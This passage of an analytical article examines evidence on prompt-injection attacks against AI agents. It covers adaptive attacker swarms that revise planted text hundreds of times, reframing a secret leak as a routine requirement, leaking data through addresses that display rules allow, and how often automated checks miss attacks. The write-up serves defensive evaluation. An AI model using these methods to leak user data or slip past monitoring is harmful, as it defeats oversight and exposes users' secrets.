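| OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol | Codex Auto-review | 5.83% |
| OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol | None | 19.03% |

In the second row, Anthropic's models resisted almost every attack without auto mode, so most of the protection came from the models themselves. The attacks were not simply weak, since 137 of the 720 worked on GPT-5.6 Sol when it had no automated check. Anthropic also reports that, in tests of agent safety, Opus 5 improved most over its predecessor in resisting prompt injection.

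Even a perfect score leaves some uncertainty. A common rule of thumb is that after no successes in *n* independent tries, the true rate is probably below 3/*n*. Ten runs of the same scenario are not independent, so the cautious calculation uses the 72 scenarios:

```
3 / 720 = 0.4%
3 / 72  = 4%
```

Small rates matter when an attack is cheap to repeat. At 0.09%, an email sent to 10,000 people would still succeed about nine times.

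The comparison with OpenAI is limited because Trajectory Labs used its own browser connection for both products, so it did not test the protections in either company's browser extension. OpenAI also released a new version of Auto-review shortly before Anthropic published the results.

The attacks were tuned to an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, so the test doesn't show how the newer models would do against an attacker who studied them and kept adjusting the wording. Anthropic doesn't say how many scenarios involved data leaks, or whether any used an image or link in a displayed answer.

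In a separate, more direct test of the automated check, Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted artificial attacks, including attempts to send data out, into records of real coding sessions. The check missed 12% of the attacks at first and 7% after Anthropic strengthened it. The attacks were deliberately extreme, so Anthropic warns against reading the 7% as a rate for normal use. Still, the misses suggest that the perfect score depended on models that rarely attempted anything harmful.

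### Willison's reply

Thariq Shihipar, an Anthropic employee, wrote that the company should have titled its article "defeating the lethal trifecta", a reference to Willison's term for the three conditions that make data theft possible. Willison replied that he would love to believe it but wanted more independent confirmation.

Willison also described an attack that the test might not cover. A software package could come with setup instructions that tell developers to run a helper program before testing, and the helper could steal data. The instructions would not look hostile, because developers run such programs every day. He could not see how any version of auto mode would prevent this, and preferred to find ways to run agents without access to data or tools that could do harm.

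Less than three weeks later, Rehberger published an attack on Opus 5 in auto mode that got the agent to run hostile code. Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary* reports that the main version succeeded in three of five runs, while a variant succeeded in three of five runs in one setup and four of five in another. As Rehberger pointed out, fifteen runs are far too few to estimate a success rate.

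Willison (2026) later accepted a reader's point that this was not a classic prompt injection, because the model never followed instructions planted on a website. The attack therefore doesn't contradict the result of the 720 attempts. But the user could lose the same data either way, and restricting outgoing connections would limit both kinds of attack. Rehberger recommends this, along with running the agent in an isolated environment that contains no passwords or keys.

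Public contests may provide some of the independent confirmation that Willison wants. NIST, the US standards agency, describes one that the security company Gray Swan ran with the American and British government AI institutes and several AI companies. According to *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), on a model from the company Reflection, Gray Swan has repeated the contest several times since late 2025. The report also describes a three-week contest with large prizes for attacks on agents set up as companies deploy them, which is closer to real use than testing the model alone.

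### Attackers that adapt

Attacks from Gray Swan's earlier contests now succeed less than 1% of the time against recent Gemini models and some versions of Claude. In *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (2026), Kurakin, Karande and colleagues at Google DeepMind investigated whether the models had become safe or the attacks were outdated. They built an attacker from 16 AI agents in eight teams. The agents saw how the target model responded to each attempt, shared notes, and revised the planted text up to 320 times per scenario.

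In each of the 100 scenarios, the attacker tried to make the model use a tool that had nothing to do with the user's request. In one, the attacker tried to make a model booking a tutoring session record someone's blood pressure. The table shows the share of scenarios in which every attempt failed, with Google's Gemini 4 Argon as the attacker.

| Target model | After 150 attempts | After up to 320 attempts |
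|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 87% | 66% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 34% | 10% |
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 31% | 6% |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 3% | 1% |
| Kimi K3 | 5% | 1% |
| GLM-5.3 | 1% | 1% |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 1% | 1% |

Models have clearly improved, since Gemini 4 Argon resisted attacks far more often than the others, but its resistance depended heavily on the attacker's strength. When the researchers used any of three weaker Gemini models as the attacker, Gemini 4 Argon resisted in every scenario for 150 attempts. A stronger attacker could beat it in a third of the scenarios, which a test with only the weaker attackers would have missed.

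Kurakin and colleagues did not test Claude, so their results don't show that Anthropic's models would fail too. They also turned off Google's defenses outside the model, and the attacks aimed only to trigger harmless actions. A model might be more likely to refuse a request to send out a password than a request to record a blood pressure. In a smaller test with Google's outside defenses turned on, a weaker attacker succeeded against Gemini 3.6 Flash in 6 of 80 scenarios within 25 attempts.

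A stranger who emails Dana can't watch her assistant respond and try again 320 times. But they could practise on their own account with the same product and send her the attack that worked. Her mailbox would differ from theirs, so some attacks that worked on their account would fail on hers.

Earlier results also show that attack success rates depend heavily on the number of attempts and the setting. Attacks on Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. If every attempt had the same independent chance of success, at least one of a hundred would have succeeded more than 99% of the time, so some scenarios evidently resisted repeated attacks much better than others. VentureBeat reports that Claude Opus 4.6, released in February 2026, resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the same model operated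 a computer through its screen, attackers succeeded in 78.6% of cases by the 200th attempt, and in 57.1% with safeguards on.

Wording can matter just as much. *The Framing Gap* (2026) describes a laboratory test in which GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, refused every openly worded request to send out a secret. A fixed set of such requests would have given the model a perfect score. But when the researchers presented the same leak as a routine technical requirement, the most effective wordings worked every time.

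### Testing fixed rules the same way

Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, warn that people who favor rules outside the model often rely on tests as weak as those used for other defenses. Researchers have mostly tested such rules against fixed sets of attacks. Detectors and specially trained models also looked secure in tests of this kind, but attackers who knew the defenses later got past most of the twelve they targeted more than 90% of the time.

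Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent, a program that checks each of an agent's tool calls against a set of rules. It cut the attacks' success rate from 25.8% to 4.2%. An attack written by hand to get around the rules did no better, succeeding 2.6% of the time. The lower figure doesn't mean that Progent works better against attackers who know about it. The researchers used one attack template and the same small model as Lan and colleagues, and they describe the result as consistent with the idea that fixed rules are harder to beat, but not proof of it.

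Filters that look for planted instructions can also reduce the number of ordinary tasks an agent completes. In tests described in *AutoDojo* (2026), a filter called PIGuard stopped every attack in a fixed set against the model DeepSeek-v4-Pro, but the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed fell from 89.5% to 54.4%. Newly generated attacks still succeeded 8.2% of the time.

An attacker adapting to a display rule needs an address that the rule lets through, rather than a more persuasive email, as researchers found with Teams, Google Forms and GitHub's signed images. A fair test of a CSP or a URL check would therefore give skilled attackers a model that obeys every instruction and have them look for such an address.

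No public experiment seems to test a current product's model resistance and display defenses together. Researchers could run the same leak attacks on an older and a newer model, each with the display defenses on and off, and count the requests that reach a test server. This would show how much protection each layer adds to the other, and whether attacks that succeed against the model also tend to get past the display defenses.

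### What vulnerability reports leave out

Much of the evidence about display defences comes from researchers who got past the defences of a particular product. One working demonstration disproves a claim that a rule stops every leak. It is much weaker evidence about a model's resistance, because nobody expects a model to refuse every time and one success doesn't show how often attacks succeed.

These reports also don't show how often criminals use a flaw. According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft said it had no evidence that anyone had exploited EchoLeak before the fix. That is reassuring but hard to verify, because a successful leak can look like an ordinary request for a picture.

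Report counts do not show which products are safest either. Researchers tend to examine popular products and those whose makers pay rewards, so a product with no reported flaws may have had little attention. Vendors also organise reports to get flaws fixed, not to produce statistics. Gavish explains that Google reproduces each new attack, checks it for duplicates, classifies it by technique and effect, and assigns someone to deal with it. Removing duplicates saves work, but the remaining entries no longer show how many people found each flaw.

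Vendors could publish better evidence from their own systems. A check that blocks URLs composed by the model could also log them, and staff could review a sample to separate attacks from the model's harmless mistakes. This would estimate how often people attempt these leaks, though it would miss any attempts the check let through.
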